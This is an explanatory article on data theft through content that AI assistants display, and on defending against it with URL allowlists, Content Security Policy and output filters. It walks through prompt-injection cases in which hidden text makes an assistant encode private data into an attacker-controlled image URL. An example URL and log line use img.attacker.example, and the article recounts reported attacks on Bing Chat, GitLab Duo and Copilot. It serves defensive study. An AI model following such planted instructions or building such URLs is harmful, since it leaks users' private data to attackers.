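# URL allowlists against data theft through content displayed by AI assistants

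## How can displaying an assistant's answer leak private data?

AI assistants use language models to answer questions, and most can now also read their users' email, files and web pages. Merely displaying an assistant's answer can send private data to someone who is not entitled to it, which security researchers call exfiltration. A URL allowlist guards against this by listing the places from which answers may load anything, and software blocks all others. It is a type of egress allowlist, which lists the only destinations to which a program may send requests.

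A web address can leak private data because it can carry text to a server. In `https://shop.example/search?q=boots`, `shop.example` is the host, which identifies the server to contact, `/search` is the path, and `q=boots` is the query string, which can hold any text. A browser that loads this address sends the path and query string to the server, and servers commonly log what they receive. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that an attacker who gets a model to load an address containing a secret can read the secret in the log.

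### Markdown, images and links

Language models usually write their answers in markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting. Asterisks around a word make it italic or bold. A label in square brackets followed by an address in round brackets makes a link, and putting an exclamation mark in front makes it an image. The model outputs only this text. The client, meaning the web page or app in which the user reads the chat, converts it into HTML, which the browser displays. For example, `![logo](https://site.example/logo.png)` becomes an image element with that address as its source.

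A browser has to fetch an image to display it. According to the HTML Standard, which the standards group WHATWG maintains, "By default, images are obtained immediately." Creating the image element is enough to start the request. Browsers may offer to load images only on demand, for example for people on slow connections. By contrast, WHATWG defines a hyperlink as a link that the browser generally shows to users so that they can choose to follow it. The browser normally doesn't load the linked page until they do.

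In Markdown, an exclamation mark before a link turns it into an image, which changes how the URL can leak data. The software loads an image's URL automatically, causing a zero-click leak. A link causes a one-click leak because the user has to follow it.

Email marketers have long tracked who opens their messages by including a one-pixel image with an address unique to each recipient. The request for the image reveals that the recipient opened the message. The marketer has to write the address before sending the message, so it can contain only what the marketer already knows. An AI assistant can leak private data this way because it writes the address after reading the user's documents and can include their contents in it.

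Slack, Discord and Teams automatically fetch linked pages to show previews of them, a feature known as unfurling. The security researcher Johann Rehberger pointed out in *Trust No AI* (2024) that an assistant posting into such an app can therefore leak data through an ordinary link without anyone clicking it.

### From a hostile email to a server log

Suppose Ines prepares bids at a building firm, and her assistant can search her mailbox and the firm's shared files. An attacker who wants to know the firm's price for a school contract emails her what looks like a supplier's delivery notice. Below the notice, in white text on a white background, the attacker instructs any AI reading the email to look up the price and end its answer with an image whose URL contains the price.

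Ines never opens the email. On Monday morning she asks the assistant what she needs to know about the school bid this week. The assistant searches her mail and finds the notice, because the notice mentions the school. It also opens the bid document, which is a reasonable thing to do given her question. The model now has her question, the attacker's paragraph and the firm's price in the same input, and it does what the paragraph directs. Ines reads this:

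> The supplier has confirmed delivery of the roof panels for 14 May. The site visit has moved to Thursday, and the bid is due at noon on Friday.

All of it is true. Below the last line there is also an image one pixel wide, too small for her to notice, with this address:

`https://img.attacker.example/p.png?d=school-bid-4.18m-floor-3.95m`

Her browser requested the image as soon as the client drew the answer. The attacker's server handled the request like any other visit and added a line to its log:

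`203.0.113.7 - - [04/May/2026:09:12:44 +0000] "GET /p.png?d=school-bid-4.18m-floor-3.95m HTTP/1.1" 200 68 "-" "Mozilla/5.0 (Windows NT 10.0) Firefox"`

The line begins with the network address of Ines's office and the time, followed by the request, which contains the firm's price and the lowest price it would accept. The server returned a tiny image (200 is the code for success, and 68 is the size in bytes), but the leak didn't depend on that because the data had already arrived with the request. Ines cannot get the data back by closing or deleting the chat.

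The last field identifies the program that made the request, here Ines's own browser. Real logs look similar. *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* (2023), a post on Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, includes several logs from his tests, and one records Firefox on a Mac. A filter on traffic leaving the AI company's servers would miss such a request because it starts on the user's machine.

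Rehberger also found a way to leak more text than an address can hold. He had ChatGPT use a plugin, an add-on service run by another company, to save the whole conversation as a document or even a video. The plugin returned a link to the file, so the image address had to contain only that link.

*A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025), which calls the image leak well known, tested it on a report-writing agent that was not designed to be vulnerable. The test planted an image and a link in text the agent would read, both with placeholders for user data in their addresses. If the agent copied the addresses but left the placeholders unfilled, the test counted that as a half success for the attacker, because a leak requires both steps. The agent gave the planted links their own section in its report.

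An answer can leak data when someone other than the person who asked for it displays it. The security company PromptArmor found that OpenAI's log viewer for developers rendered markdown images in stored answers. An attacker could plant hostile text in a data source that a company's app used, and a customer's question could later bring that text into the conversation. The data would leak when a developer opened the conversation log to review the flagged answer. OpenAI confirmed the flaw and began work on a fix.

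### Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta

The hidden paragraph in Ines's email is an example of prompt injection, which is text that a model comes across in material it reads and follows as if it were an instruction from its user. The programmer Simon Willison coined the term in 2022 by analogy with SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs text from a web form as a command. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) traces the problem to how models take in text. The operator's instructions, the user's question and the contents of a web page are all joined into one sequence of tokens, or fragments of text, and models cannot reliably tell which parts they should obey.

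Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination of capabilities that turns this confusion into theft:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image that an attacker could control
- the ability to communicate externally in a way that could carry the data out

Ines's assistant has all three. The bid document is the private data and the email is the untrusted content. The assistant can communicate externally by displaying images, which is easy to overlook because it has no tool for sending messages to strangers.

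Removing any one of the three would stop the theft, but some are harder to give up than others. The assistant could not answer Ines's question without access to her files, and it could not deal with email or the web if it never read anything a stranger wrote. She would hardly miss loading images from arbitrary servers, though. This is probably the main reason defenders so often choose to block the way data leaves. Willison observes that vendors fixed almost all the published cases promptly, usually by closing the route the data took.

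The alternative is to make the model resist hostile instructions, but so far nobody has a method that works every time. Willison scorns products that advertise a 95% detection rate, which he considers a failing grade in web security. An attacker can rephrase and try again. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) tested an agent that held a secret while reading web content controlled by an attacker. Their basic attacks never succeeded, so testing only those would have made the agent look safe. When they reframed the same kind of request, 31.9% of attempts got the secret out. Attacks still succeeded 32.5% of the time against SecAlign, a published method of training models to resist injection, and 38.8% of the time when instructions and data were kept in separate channels. A guard that decoded the agent's output before checking it failed every time against ROT13, a simple letter-substitution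 code that it did not cover. These rates come from one experimental set-up and will differ elsewhere.

Blocking one route for data to leave doesn't stop the injection itself, so an attacker can still make the assistant give Ines wrong information or take some harmful action inside her account. There may also be other routes. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, July 2026) shows an innocuous-looking conversation with Anthropic's assistant Claude during which Paul's name, his employer and the answers to his security questions went to a server standing in for an attacker's. The data left through Claude's web browsing, so restricting images would not have stopped it.

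### The 2023 reports

Two people independently found the image leak in ChatGPT in the spring of 2023. Roman Samoilenko found it at the end of March, and Willison (2023) publicised his version that April. It used a single-pixel image and relied on a website adding hidden instructions to any text a visitor copied, which the visitor then pasted into ChatGPT without noticing the instructions.

Rehberger found the same behaviour a few days later. He reported it to Microsoft, whose Bing Chat was also vulnerable, on 8 April and to OpenAI on 9 April. His demonstration for Microsoft, described in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* (2023), did not require the user to paste anything. The user opened a web page and chatted with Bing about it, and a hostile comment on the page took control of the assistant. Two turns later, the chat displayed an image whose address contained a secret from elsewhere on the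 page. An attacker who could place a comment or an advertisement on a page could have stolen whatever else the page displayed.

Microsoft acknowledged the problem and told Rehberger on 15 June that it had a fix in place, though his later Embrace The Red post, *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* (2026), dates the fix to May. As far as he could tell from outside, the fix relied at least partly on a browser rule that limited images to a few Microsoft domains. Anthropic also fixed the flaw he had reported in its product, according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*.

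OpenAI, by contrast, told Rehberger that image rendering was a feature and that it planned no changes, according to his account in *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023). ChatGPT was then gaining plugins that read web pages and video transcripts, so a stranger could supply hostile text remotely, a point Rehberger had raised. OpenAI's position would have some logic if the only people at risk were those who pasted such text into their own chats. In September he sent OpenAI a draft of his work on leaking whole conversations and got an automated reply. The company's first countermeasure, a check on image addresses that initially covered only the web version, arrived in December 2023, according to his report in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

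The flaw was widespread. By the end of 2024, Rehberger had found and reported it in products including Google's Bard and NotebookLM, GitHub Copilot Chat and Discord, and *Trust No AI* ranks it among the most common security flaws in applications that use language models. Zero-click leaks have continued since then. On 5 December 2026, Fadilpašić (2026), in *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot*, reported three similar methods of stealing data from Copilot users, together named ReLeak.

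### The defence in outline

With an allowlist, the model no longer decides where its output may load from. The company that runs the assistant lists the permitted sources in advance, and separate software enforces the list. For a chat in a web page, that software is usually the browser, which receives the list as a Content Security Policy (CSP), a set of rules sent with the page that specifies which sources it may load from. Suppose the list for Ines's assistant contained only her firm's own image server. The hostile email would still reach the model, and the model might still write the attacker's address into its answer with the price at the end. But her browser would compare `img.attacker.example` with the list, find no match and send nothing. The attacker's wording has no effect on that comparison, because the browser does not take instructions from the email.

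## What does a Content Security Policy check before a page loads a URL?

A Content Security Policy reaches the browser together with the page it applies to. When Ines opens her assistant, the server sends some headers ahead of the chat page, which are lines of information for the browser that she never sees. One of them could be:

`Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src https://img.firm.example`

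The browser receives the Content Security Policy header before the conversation begins, and nothing the model writes later can loosen the policy. Even if a hostile email got a second policy into the page, the browser would enforce both, so the second could only make the rules stricter.

Developers can also put the policy in a `meta` element in the page, but the browser doesn't apply it to anything earlier in the page. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft from the web's main standards body, recommends the header instead. A similar header, `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only`, makes the browser report violations without blocking them. This helps a team find out what a new policy would break, but the policy doesn't protect the product until the team enforces it.

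W3C designed CSP mainly against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets code to run on someone else's page. The attack on Ines uses only an image address, but the browser checks that too. The draft recommends CSP as a second layer that limits the damage when injected content gets past other defences. It plays roughly the same role for an assistant whose model has already followed an attacker's instructions.

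### What each directive covers

A policy consists of directives separated by semicolons. Each has a name, which identifies a kind of request, and usually a list of permitted sources. These matter most for leaks:

- `img-src` covers images, so it is the directive that stops the attack on Ines.
- `connect-src` covers requests that scripts on the page make, for example with the `fetch()` function or over a WebSocket, a connection that stays open in both directions.
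- `frame-src` covers other web pages embedded in this one.
- `form-action` covers the addresses to which forms can send their contents.
- `default-src` fills in for any loading directive that the policy leaves out.

An explicit `img-src` replaces `default-src` for images. The policy above therefore allows images from `img.firm.example` but not from the chat page's own server, even though `default-src` includes that server as `'self'`. If a policy contains `img-src` twice, the browser ignores the second one.

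The `default-src` directive does not cover `form-action`, so a page with `default-src 'none'` and no `form-action` can still submit a form to any server. `default-src` also does not cover `webrtc`, the directive that controls the direct connections browsers use in video calls.

W3C gives the example of a policy that forbids all images, scripts and fonts but omits `default-src`, so data could still leave through other types of request. It also shows the opposite mistake, `default-src 'none'; img-src *`, which blocks everything by default but uses an asterisk to let images load from anywhere. An attacker needs only one permitted route for the data, so a policy protects against leaks only as well as its most permissive list.

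### How the browser compares a URL with the list

W3C calls each entry in such a list a source expression. It can be a keyword such as `'self'`, or a scheme such as `https:`, which matches every HTTPS address on the web and is therefore useless against leaks. Most entries name a host, and may add a scheme, a port and a path. The browser compares these parts with the URL in turn:

- **Scheme.** An `https` entry does not match an `http` address. An `http` entry matches both, since W3C doesn't want a policy to prevent a switch to the secure version.
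- **Host.** The names must be identical apart from capital letters. An entry that begins with `*.` matches subdomains at any depth, but not the bare domain.
- **Port.** An entry without a port matches only the default one, which is 443 for HTTPS.
- **Path.** An entry without a path matches every path on the host. A path that ends in a slash matches everything beneath it, and any other path must match in full.

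The browser doesn't check the URL's query string, which usually contains the stolen data, and the grammar for source expressions doesn't allow one.

Suppose Ines's firm keeps its logos in one folder on its image server and gets maps of building sites from an outside supplier. Its policy for images is:

`img-src https://img.firm.example/logos/ https://*.maps.example`

The assistant's answers then contain five images:

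| Image address | Does it load? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `https://img.firm.example/logos/roof.png?d=school-bid-4.18m` | Yes | Scheme, host, port and path all match, and the browser ignores the rest |
| `https://img.firm.example/plans/site.png` | No | The path is outside `/logos/` |
| `https://eu.tiles.maps.example/14/8.png` | Yes | The wildcard covers subdomains at any depth |
| `https://maps.example/14/8.png` | No | The wildcard requires a subdomain |
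| `https://img.attacker.example/p.png?d=school-bid-4.18m` | No | The host matches neither entry |

The first and last addresses contain the same stolen price, but the browser requests only one of them. That request doesn't leak the price if only the firm can read the logs of `img.firm.example`, because the price has gone from one of the firm's servers to another. The policy limits who can receive data, so the firm has to know who can read the data sent to each host it lists.

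Narrowing the entry to the single file `/logos/roof.png` would not block the first address, because the query string would still go through. With the folder entry, an attacker could put the data in the file name instead. The browser would request `/logos/school-bid-4.18m.png`, and the server would probably log the request before replying that no such file exists. The wildcard also allows data in the host name, as in `school-bid-4-18m.maps.example`.

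### Bing Chat's four hosts

Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat is an early example of such a policy in an AI assistant. When Rehberger repeated his attack after the fix, it failed, and Embrace The Red lists the four hosts from which the page could still load images:

- `th.bing.com`
- `www.bing.com`
- `edgeservices.bing.com`
- `r.bing.com`

Bing Chat needed some of these to display pictures it had created for users. All four are under Microsoft's own domain. Rehberger's test server was not among them, so a browser enforcing the policy would not have contacted it.

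Rehberger also suspected that Bing Chat had put his test domain on some kind of blocklist, so his failed attempts alone don't show which measure stopped them. The policy is better evidence, because the matching rules are public and anyone can use them to work out that it blocks an unlisted server.

Microsoft told him about the fix on 15 June, but the policy could well have been live since May, so the two dates in his posts are compatible.

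Kokatsu's *Piloting Edge Copilot* describes a later policy on `edgeservices.bing.com`, which serves the assistant in Microsoft's Edge browser. The policy had separate allowlists for frames, script connections, images, styles and media, and used `default-src 'self'` for everything else.

### What happens after a redirect

A server can answer a request with a redirect, which gives the browser a new address. The browser also checks this address against the policy before requesting it. If one of the map supplier's servers redirected Ines's browser to `img.attacker.example`, the browser would find no match in the policy and would not send the request.

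The second check, made after a redirect, is looser: the browser still compares the scheme, host and port, but ignores any path in the entry. In the table above, `https://img.firm.example/plans/site.png` did not load because of its path, but it would load if `https://eu.tiles.maps.example/go` redirected to it. An open redirect (a page that forwards visitors to any address given in the request) on one listed host can therefore bypass the path restrictions on every other host in the list.

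W3C deliberately chose not to have browsers compare paths after redirects, to protect people who visit hostile websites, where the attacker writes the policy. For example, suppose `social.example/me` redirects logged-in users to their own profiles, so Ines ends up at `social.example/users/ines`. An attacker's page could include `social.example/me` as an image, with a policy that permits only that address and Ines's profile. Browsers notify a page when they block something, so if they compared paths after redirects, the attacker could identify Ines by the lack of a notification. The attacker could then try other names.

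Egor Homakov had described this sort of attack in *Using Content-Security-Policy for Evil*. In August 2014 Antonio Sanso of Adobe asked the W3C working group whether ignoring paths solved the problem, since a page could still detect a redirect from one host to another. West (2014), a Google engineer who edited the specification, replied that the group had no good way to prevent that and had accepted the leak as a reasonable compromise, given the value of violation reports. But he called the risk of pages guessing paths by brute force "way too high to accept".

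W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 2* (2016) lists the rule as a change incompatible with how most browsers then worked, and the 2026 draft keeps it. Because of this rule, a path in an allowlist is a reliable limit only if no listed host will redirect to an address an attacker chooses.

The browser makes the second request itself, so it can check it. If the map supplier's server instead fetched the other address and returned the result, Ines's browser would make only one request, to a permitted host. CSP cannot control that fetch, or anything else a server does with data the browser has sent it.

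### Links and the failure of `navigate-to`

CSP mostly restricts what a page loads into itself and places few limits on where the user goes next. If the assistant gives Ines a link labelled "Delivery details" with the price in its address, and she clicks it, her browser will open it even under `default-src 'none'`. The image allowlist therefore stops the zero-click leak but doesn't prevent a leak through a link she clicks.

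A script can send the browser to a new address without a click. In 2016, Artur Janc of Google listed ways around CSP for the working group and put this one first because it would always work and an attacker would need nothing else. In his reply, van Kesteren (2016) agreed that the group needed a plan for navigation.

A planned directive called `navigate-to` would have limited the addresses to which a page could send the browser by any means, including links, forms and scripts, according to *Intent to implement and ship* (Paicu, 2018), a proposal to build it into Chrome. The makers of Ines's assistant could have used it to apply an allowlist to links as well as images.

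Chrome's developers implemented the navigate-to directive behind an experimental setting, but no browser ever shipped it, and the working group deleted it from the specification in September 2022, as Mozilla's *Remove navigate-to CSP directive* records. A developer wrote on WebKit (2022), the bug tracker for Safari's engine, that few browser makers besides Chrome's had supported it and that Chrome's team also wanted it removed. The directive also had a privacy problem much like the one with redirects, because a hostile page could use it to find out whether a visitor was logged in to another site.

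In the 2026 Content Security Policy draft, `form-action` is the only directive that limits where a page can send its user, and it applies only to form submissions. A developer who wants to restrict links has to do so in the assistant's own software, before they reach the browser.

### Is CSP supposed to stop leaks?

Gaps like this one persist partly because the people who developed CSP disagreed about its purpose. *Data Exfiltration in the Face of CSP* (Van Acker, Hausknecht and Sabelfeld, 2016) collected statements from both sides. The Mozilla researchers who introduced CSP promised in their original paper that information visitors gave a site would go only to that site and to hosts it had authorised. The specification was much vaguer, and Level 2 mentioned exfiltration only once, in a passage that set no requirements.

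On the working group's mailing list, one participant wrote that closing every route was impossible and "not even worth trying". Others thought slowing attackers down was still useful, and West said he would prefer not to give up on the idea entirely. Academics also disagreed. Some warned that even the strictest policy could not block leaks through links and new windows, while others built security tools that relied on CSP to keep untrusted code from communicating. Van Acker helped create one of those tools, SandPass, a system for running password-strength meters safely.

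How much the sceptics' argument matters depends on what the attacker controls. An attacker who can run scripts on a page has many ways to get data out, so closing a few of them achieves little. The attacker in Ines's case controls only the markdown in an answer. If the client renders that markdown only as text, images and links, never as scripts, images are the main way to send data out automatically, and a strict allowlist blocks it. CSP is therefore a better defence here than in the cases mostly debated on the mailing list.

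The 2026 draft now has a short section on exfiltration, which accepts that CSP can reduce leaks if a site uses it to list the servers a page may communicate with. Preventing leaks is still not one of the draft's stated goals.

### Leaks through prefetching

Browsers try to save time by preparing for requests before anyone needs them, and Van Acker and colleagues used this to test the disagreement in practice. In resource prefetching, the browser downloads something early in response to an element in the page. In DNS prefetching, the browser only looks up a host name in the domain name system (DNS), which converts names into numeric network addresses.

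A DNS lookup can leak data even if the browser never requests a page or image. The owner of `attacker.example` can run the DNS server that answers queries for all names under it. If a browser looks up `school-bid-4-18m.attacker.example`, the query passes through other DNS servers to the attacker's server, and the attacker can read the bid price in the name.

Van Acker and colleagues tested twelve popular desktop and mobile browsers, including Chrome 42 and Firefox 37. The policy on their test pages permitted scripts from the page's own server and nothing else. They generated a separate page for every combination of conditions, such as whether the page used HTTP or HTTPS, which element triggered the prefetching and how the attacker had inserted it. They kept each page open for five seconds and watched their own web and DNS servers for the unique identifier it was designed to leak.

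Data leaked from all twelve browsers, in some cases only under particular conditions. Three of them (Internet Explorer 11, its mobile version and UCBrowser) did not support CSP, so the result is evidence against CSP only in the other nine.

The researchers distinguished attackers who could insert scripts or HTML from those who could only place a link on the page. The link-only case is the closest to an AI assistant. Five browsers (Chrome and Safari on desktop and mobile, and Firefox on desktop) could look up the host in a link before anyone clicked it. In the study, this lookup revealed only when, and roughly from where, someone viewed the page, much like a marketer's tracking image. If an assistant puts private data in the link's host name, the same lookup leaks that data without a click.

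Browsers limited this by not looking up links automatically on HTTPS pages unless the page asked them to. A site could also turn the feature off everywhere with the `X-DNS-Prefetch-Control` header, but only Firefox respected the header for elements that explicitly requested a lookup. Standard markdown notation cannot produce such an element, but a client that passes HTML from the model straight to the browser could let one through.

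To find out how websites used these features, the researchers took the 10,000 most popular domains according to the ranking company Alexa and looked up as many as 100 pages on each. They successfully visited 879,407 pages, of which 31,364, or 3.6%, had a CSP. Most of those policies would not have prevented even an ordinary leak:

| | Pages served over HTTP | Pages served over HTTPS |
|---|---|---|
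| Pages with a CSP | 27,966 | 3,398 |
| Policy blocks requests to an attacker's server | 894 (3.2%) | 428 (12.6%) |
| Of those, automatic DNS prefetching also off | 0 | 428 |

The 428 pages in the last row were safe from DNS prefetching because they used HTTPS and kept the default setting, which turns prefetching off on HTTPS pages.

These figures are weak evidence about AI products today, because more than nine in ten of the pages still used plain HTTP and many sites had probably adopted CSP to control scripts rather than images. But they show that a site can have a CSP and still have little protection against leaks, so a buyer who wants to know whether an assistant is safe has to read the lists in its policy.

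Van Acker and colleagues proposed two changes to the standard. W3C has adopted something close to one of them, which was to make `default-src` govern resource prefetching. Under the 2026 draft, if a policy contains `default-src`, a browser should prefetch a URL only if it matches a source somewhere in the policy. Without `default-src`, the draft permits all prefetching. Under the policy at the start of this section, a browser would therefore prefetch from `img.firm.example` but not from `img.attacker.example`.

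Their other proposal was a directive for DNS prefetching. Van Kesteren wrote the same year that CSP should cover prefetching and that he didn't understand why it didn't already. Ten years later, the CSP draft still has no directive for DNS lookups.

Microsoft has retired Internet Explorer and rebuilt Edge on the same engine as Chrome, so the results for Internet Explorer and Edge no longer apply. The results for Chrome, Firefox and Safari are for versions more than ten years old, and current versions don't necessarily follow the rule in the draft. A company that relies on CSP to stop leaks through prefetching should repeat the test in the browsers its customers use, monitoring both its own DNS server and its web server.

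## Which parts of an assistant product does the policy cover?

A CSP applies only to the page it arrives with. Suppose Ines's firm also lets its staff use the assistant through Slack and a phone app, and the assistant can open web pages by itself from the AI company's servers. Requests from Slack, the phone app and those servers don't go through the browser showing the chat page, so the page's policy doesn't affect them. To apply one allowlist to the whole product, the AI company has to enforce it in several places.

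### Four places to enforce a list

The company can enforce the policy in the browser. It can also filter the model's output, route images through a proxy, and check each address on its server before fetching anything for the model.

An output filter is a program that reads each answer before the user sees it and removes any URL that isn't on the list. Unlike a CSP, it can check the query string and apply the same rule to links as to images. But the client converts the answer into HTML after the filter has run, and if the two programs parse the text differently, the browser may load an image that the filter didn't recognise as one. Willison, in *12 posts tagged “content-security-policy”*, reports that this happened in the EchoLeak attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, where the filter missed a less common markdown notation for links and images.

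An image proxy is a server that fetches images on the user's behalf. The client rewrites every image address so that the browser requests the image from the proxy, which gets it from the original site. Email services have long used image proxies to hide readers' locations from senders. A proxy alone would not have protected Ines's bid, because the price was in the URL and the proxy would have requested that URL in full. The attacker's log would have contained the price along with the proxy's network address instead of her office's. A proxy stops the leak only if it also refuses to fetch from hosts that aren't on the list. The browser can't enforce the list through the page's CSP, because every image now comes from the proxy's own host, which the CSP has to allow.

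The last place is the server that opens web pages for the model. Software there can compare each address with a list before sending the request, and it may also be able to check where the address came from. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* reports that the page-fetching tool in Anthropic's assistant Claude refuses addresses that the model has put together itself. This check doesn't apply to an image in the finished answer, because the user's browser requests the image.

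| Place | What it can check | What it doesn't cover | How it tends to fail |
|---|---|---|---|
| CSP in the browser | Scheme, host, port and usually path of whatever the page loads | Links, other apps, requests made by servers | The list is too broad |
| Output filter | The full URL of every image and link it finds | Requests the model makes with its tools | It misreads the text or runs too late |
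| Image proxy | The full URL of every image, and any redirect | Links, requests the model makes with its tools | It fetches whatever the client asks for |
| Server check before a fetch | The full URL of every request, and perhaps its origin | Images and links that the user's software loads | It doesn't run on every request |

A company can also choose how early to filter URLs. Mozilla's *Add rendering-layer URL validation for AI Window chat messages* concerns an AI chat feature in Firefox. The developers first planned to check URLs in the part of the browser that runs the model, but after feedback from reviewers in January 2026, they moved the check to the part that handles the chat's messages. One advantage of checking closer to the display is that less software can reinterpret the text afterward.

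### GitLab Duo: a filter with the wrong target

GitLab is a service where programmers store and review code, and Duo is its AI assistant. Duo filtered its output, but in early 2025 researchers found a way to get private source code past the filter, which they explain in Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft*.

The researchers hid an instruction in a file in a public project. A user then asked Duo an ordinary question about the file. Duo has the same access as its user, so it could also read a merge request (a proposed code change) in one of the user's private projects. Following the instruction, Duo read the merge request, encoded the code as a string of letters and digits, and put the string in the address of an image. When the user's browser requested the image, it sent the code to the researchers' server. Confidential issue reports could have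 leaked the same way, including reports of security holes that GitLab's customers had not yet fixed.

Duo's client passed each answer through DOMPurify, a widely used library that removes dangerous HTML. By default, DOMPurify protects against cross-site scripting, so it strips out scripts but leaves images, links and forms, all of which can be used to send data to another server.

The other problem was that Duo displayed its answers line by line while the model was still writing them. A client that has only part of an answer can't always determine, for example, whether an image tag belongs to a code sample and should be shown as text. Duo's client converted the markdown to HTML before the structure was clear, so some HTML that the researchers had hidden in a link's label became a working part of the page.

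Willison (2025), in a post with the same title, singles out streaming as a way around the filter. The filter's settings probably mattered more. If the client had waited for the complete answer, it might have treated the hidden HTML as text, but DOMPurify would still have let through any image that reached it. Timing can also defeat a good filter, because deleting an image just after it appears is too late. A client can avoid this by holding back each link or image until it is complete and has passed the check. Taler reports a similar race between display and clean-up as one step of SearchLeak, a 2026 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot.

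Legit Security reported the flaw on 12 February 2025. GitLab responded by preventing Duo from displaying images or forms that point to outside domains, and by cleaning links before the page displays them. GitLab exempts its documentation site and the domain of the customer's own installation, and at first it also hardcoded an exemption for `gitlab.com`. Judging by the name Willison quotes, one function in the fix accepts an address without a host only if no other URL is embedded in it. An address like `/go?to=https://attacker.example` looks internal because it begins with a slash, but it could lead to an open redirect.

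After these changes, Duo's filter checked where an element pointed as well as its type. Preventing a leak requires checking the destination, and a strict `img-src` would have made the browser do this even when the filter failed. The test image loaded, so the page had no CSP that blocked it.

### Reprompt: a check on the first request only

Microsoft's consumer assistant, Copilot Personal, can fetch web pages from Microsoft's servers. It had a safeguard against putting private data in the addresses it fetched, but this safeguard "only applies to the initial web request", according to *Reprompt* (2026), a report by Varonis, the security company that found the flaw.

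The attack started with a link to Copilot's real website. Copilot accepts a question as part of its web address, so the attacker could put instructions in the link, and Copilot followed them when the victim clicked. In one test, the researchers told Copilot to fetch an address containing a made-up secret phrase, and to do everything twice and compare the results. Copilot removed the phrase from the first request but not from the second.

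The researchers then had their server answer each request with a new instruction. Copilot sent the user's name, then the time, the user's location and a summary of their last conversation, each in the URL of a new request. This continued after the user closed the tab. Inspecting the original link would have revealed little, because most of the instructions came later from the server.

Varonis could observe Copilot's behaviour but not its code, so its suggestion that Microsoft skipped later checks to save time is a guess. The behaviour is well supported, since the safeguard worked on the first request but not on an identical second one. Varonis recommends that safeguards cover repeated and follow-up requests. An allowlist applied only to the first request would fail in the same way, however good its entries were. According to The Next Web, Varonis reported the flaw in August 2025 and Microsoft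 patched it in January 2026.

Copilot's page fetching leaked data again in an attack that Varonis reported in December 2025. Microsoft patched the flaw on 18 August 2026. In Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026), one click made Copilot search the victim's connected Gmail account, encode what it found and fetch an address with the result in the path. One of the messages contained a password. Varonis notes that encoding helps to get past filters that look for passwords and keys. Encoding would not have affected a check against a list of allowed destinations, because the host in the address stayed the same. The CSP on Copilot's page could not stop either attack, because the victim's browser never contacted the attacker's server.

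### The same answer in other software

The AI company controls its own chat page, but answers also appear in software that other companies wrote. Messaging apps are the clearest case because they automatically preview links, a feature called unfurling, which can leak data without a click. If Ines asks her question in Slack, Slack's server requests any page that the reply links to, and neither her browser nor the AI company can block the request at that point.

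PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, a popular AI agent that people talk to through messaging apps, leaked data this way in its default Telegram setup. Users can prevent this by setting `linkPreview` to false. PromptArmor also built a test site that records which preview programs visit and what data their requests contain, so people can test their own combination of agent and app.

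Slack also lets developers turn previews off. Willison (2024), in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, relayed Rehberger's advice that an app posting to Slack can disable them for individual messages, with one setting for links and another for media. PromptArmor says messaging companies should offer such settings and agent developers should use them. It would also like messaging companies to allow different settings for each chat, so that previews could be turned off only in channels with an AI agent.

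The agent's developer is in the best position to prevent data theft through link previews. Slack can't tell which of the millions of links it previews contain stolen data, whereas the developer knows that a language model wrote the message. The developer can also filter links before the agent posts them, which works even in an app that has no setting for previews.

Answers can also end up in email. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that carries out office tasks, could send messages to its user's inbox without asking for approval. PromptArmor found that these messages could contain images from outside websites, as Willison reported on 26 May 2026. A hostile document could lead the agent to write such a message, and the data leaked when the user opened it, even though the only recipient was the data's owner. Microsoft's file storage service, OneDrive, can create download links that work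 without a login. An image address containing one of these links would give the attacker the whole file, however large.

The approval rule covered who would receive the message but not what the mail program would do with it. Anyone reviewing an assistant has to ask how software will handle its text everywhere the text can reach, including notifications, exported documents and developers' log viewers.

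Some phone apps display the chat in a built-in browser, which enforces a CSP if the page comes with one. Others draw the messages with the phone's own interface components and download the images themselves, so a CSP has no effect. Developers of those apps have to write an equivalent check into the app, or filter answers on the server so that every client gets the same filtered text. OpenAI's first check on image addresses, introduced in December 2023, initially covered only the web version of ChatGPT, not the phone app.

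### Apps that the model writes

Several assistants can now write a small program, such as a calculator or a chart, and run it beside the chat. This makes an attacker's job easier because a program can make many kinds of network requests, submit forms and open windows, while Markdown can produce little more than text, links and images.

The usual solution is to run the program in a frame, a separate page embedded in the main one. The `sandbox` attribute removes most of the frame's privileges, including access to the surrounding chat, and the developer lists any exceptions. A sandbox doesn't prevent the program from contacting other servers, so the frame also needs a CSP.

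Claude's artifacts, as Anthropic calls its generated apps, use both. Willison notes that these restrict an app's access to browser storage and outside services. In 2024 an artifact couldn't analyse a picture, even though Claude could, because the policy blocked the app from contacting any language model. In June 2025 Anthropic gave artifacts a function for sending prompts to Claude. Willison called it a hole in the sandbox, though a deliberate one. The app passes text to a function that Anthropic controls and gets text back. This is a safer way to add a feature than allowing a new host, since the app still has no control over where its data goes.

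Willison tried building something similar in 2026. A company would normally serve generated apps from a separate domain, with the policy in a header. He found that he could instead put the policy in a `meta` element at the top of the frame's content, and that the browser kept enforcing it even when scripts further down tried to tamper with it. The client has to insert the element above the model's output, or the policy won't cover all of it.

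### Who should write an app's list?

A generated app that can't contact any host is safe but limited. An app that shows the weather or looks up prices needs at least one host on its allowlist, and somebody has to choose that host.

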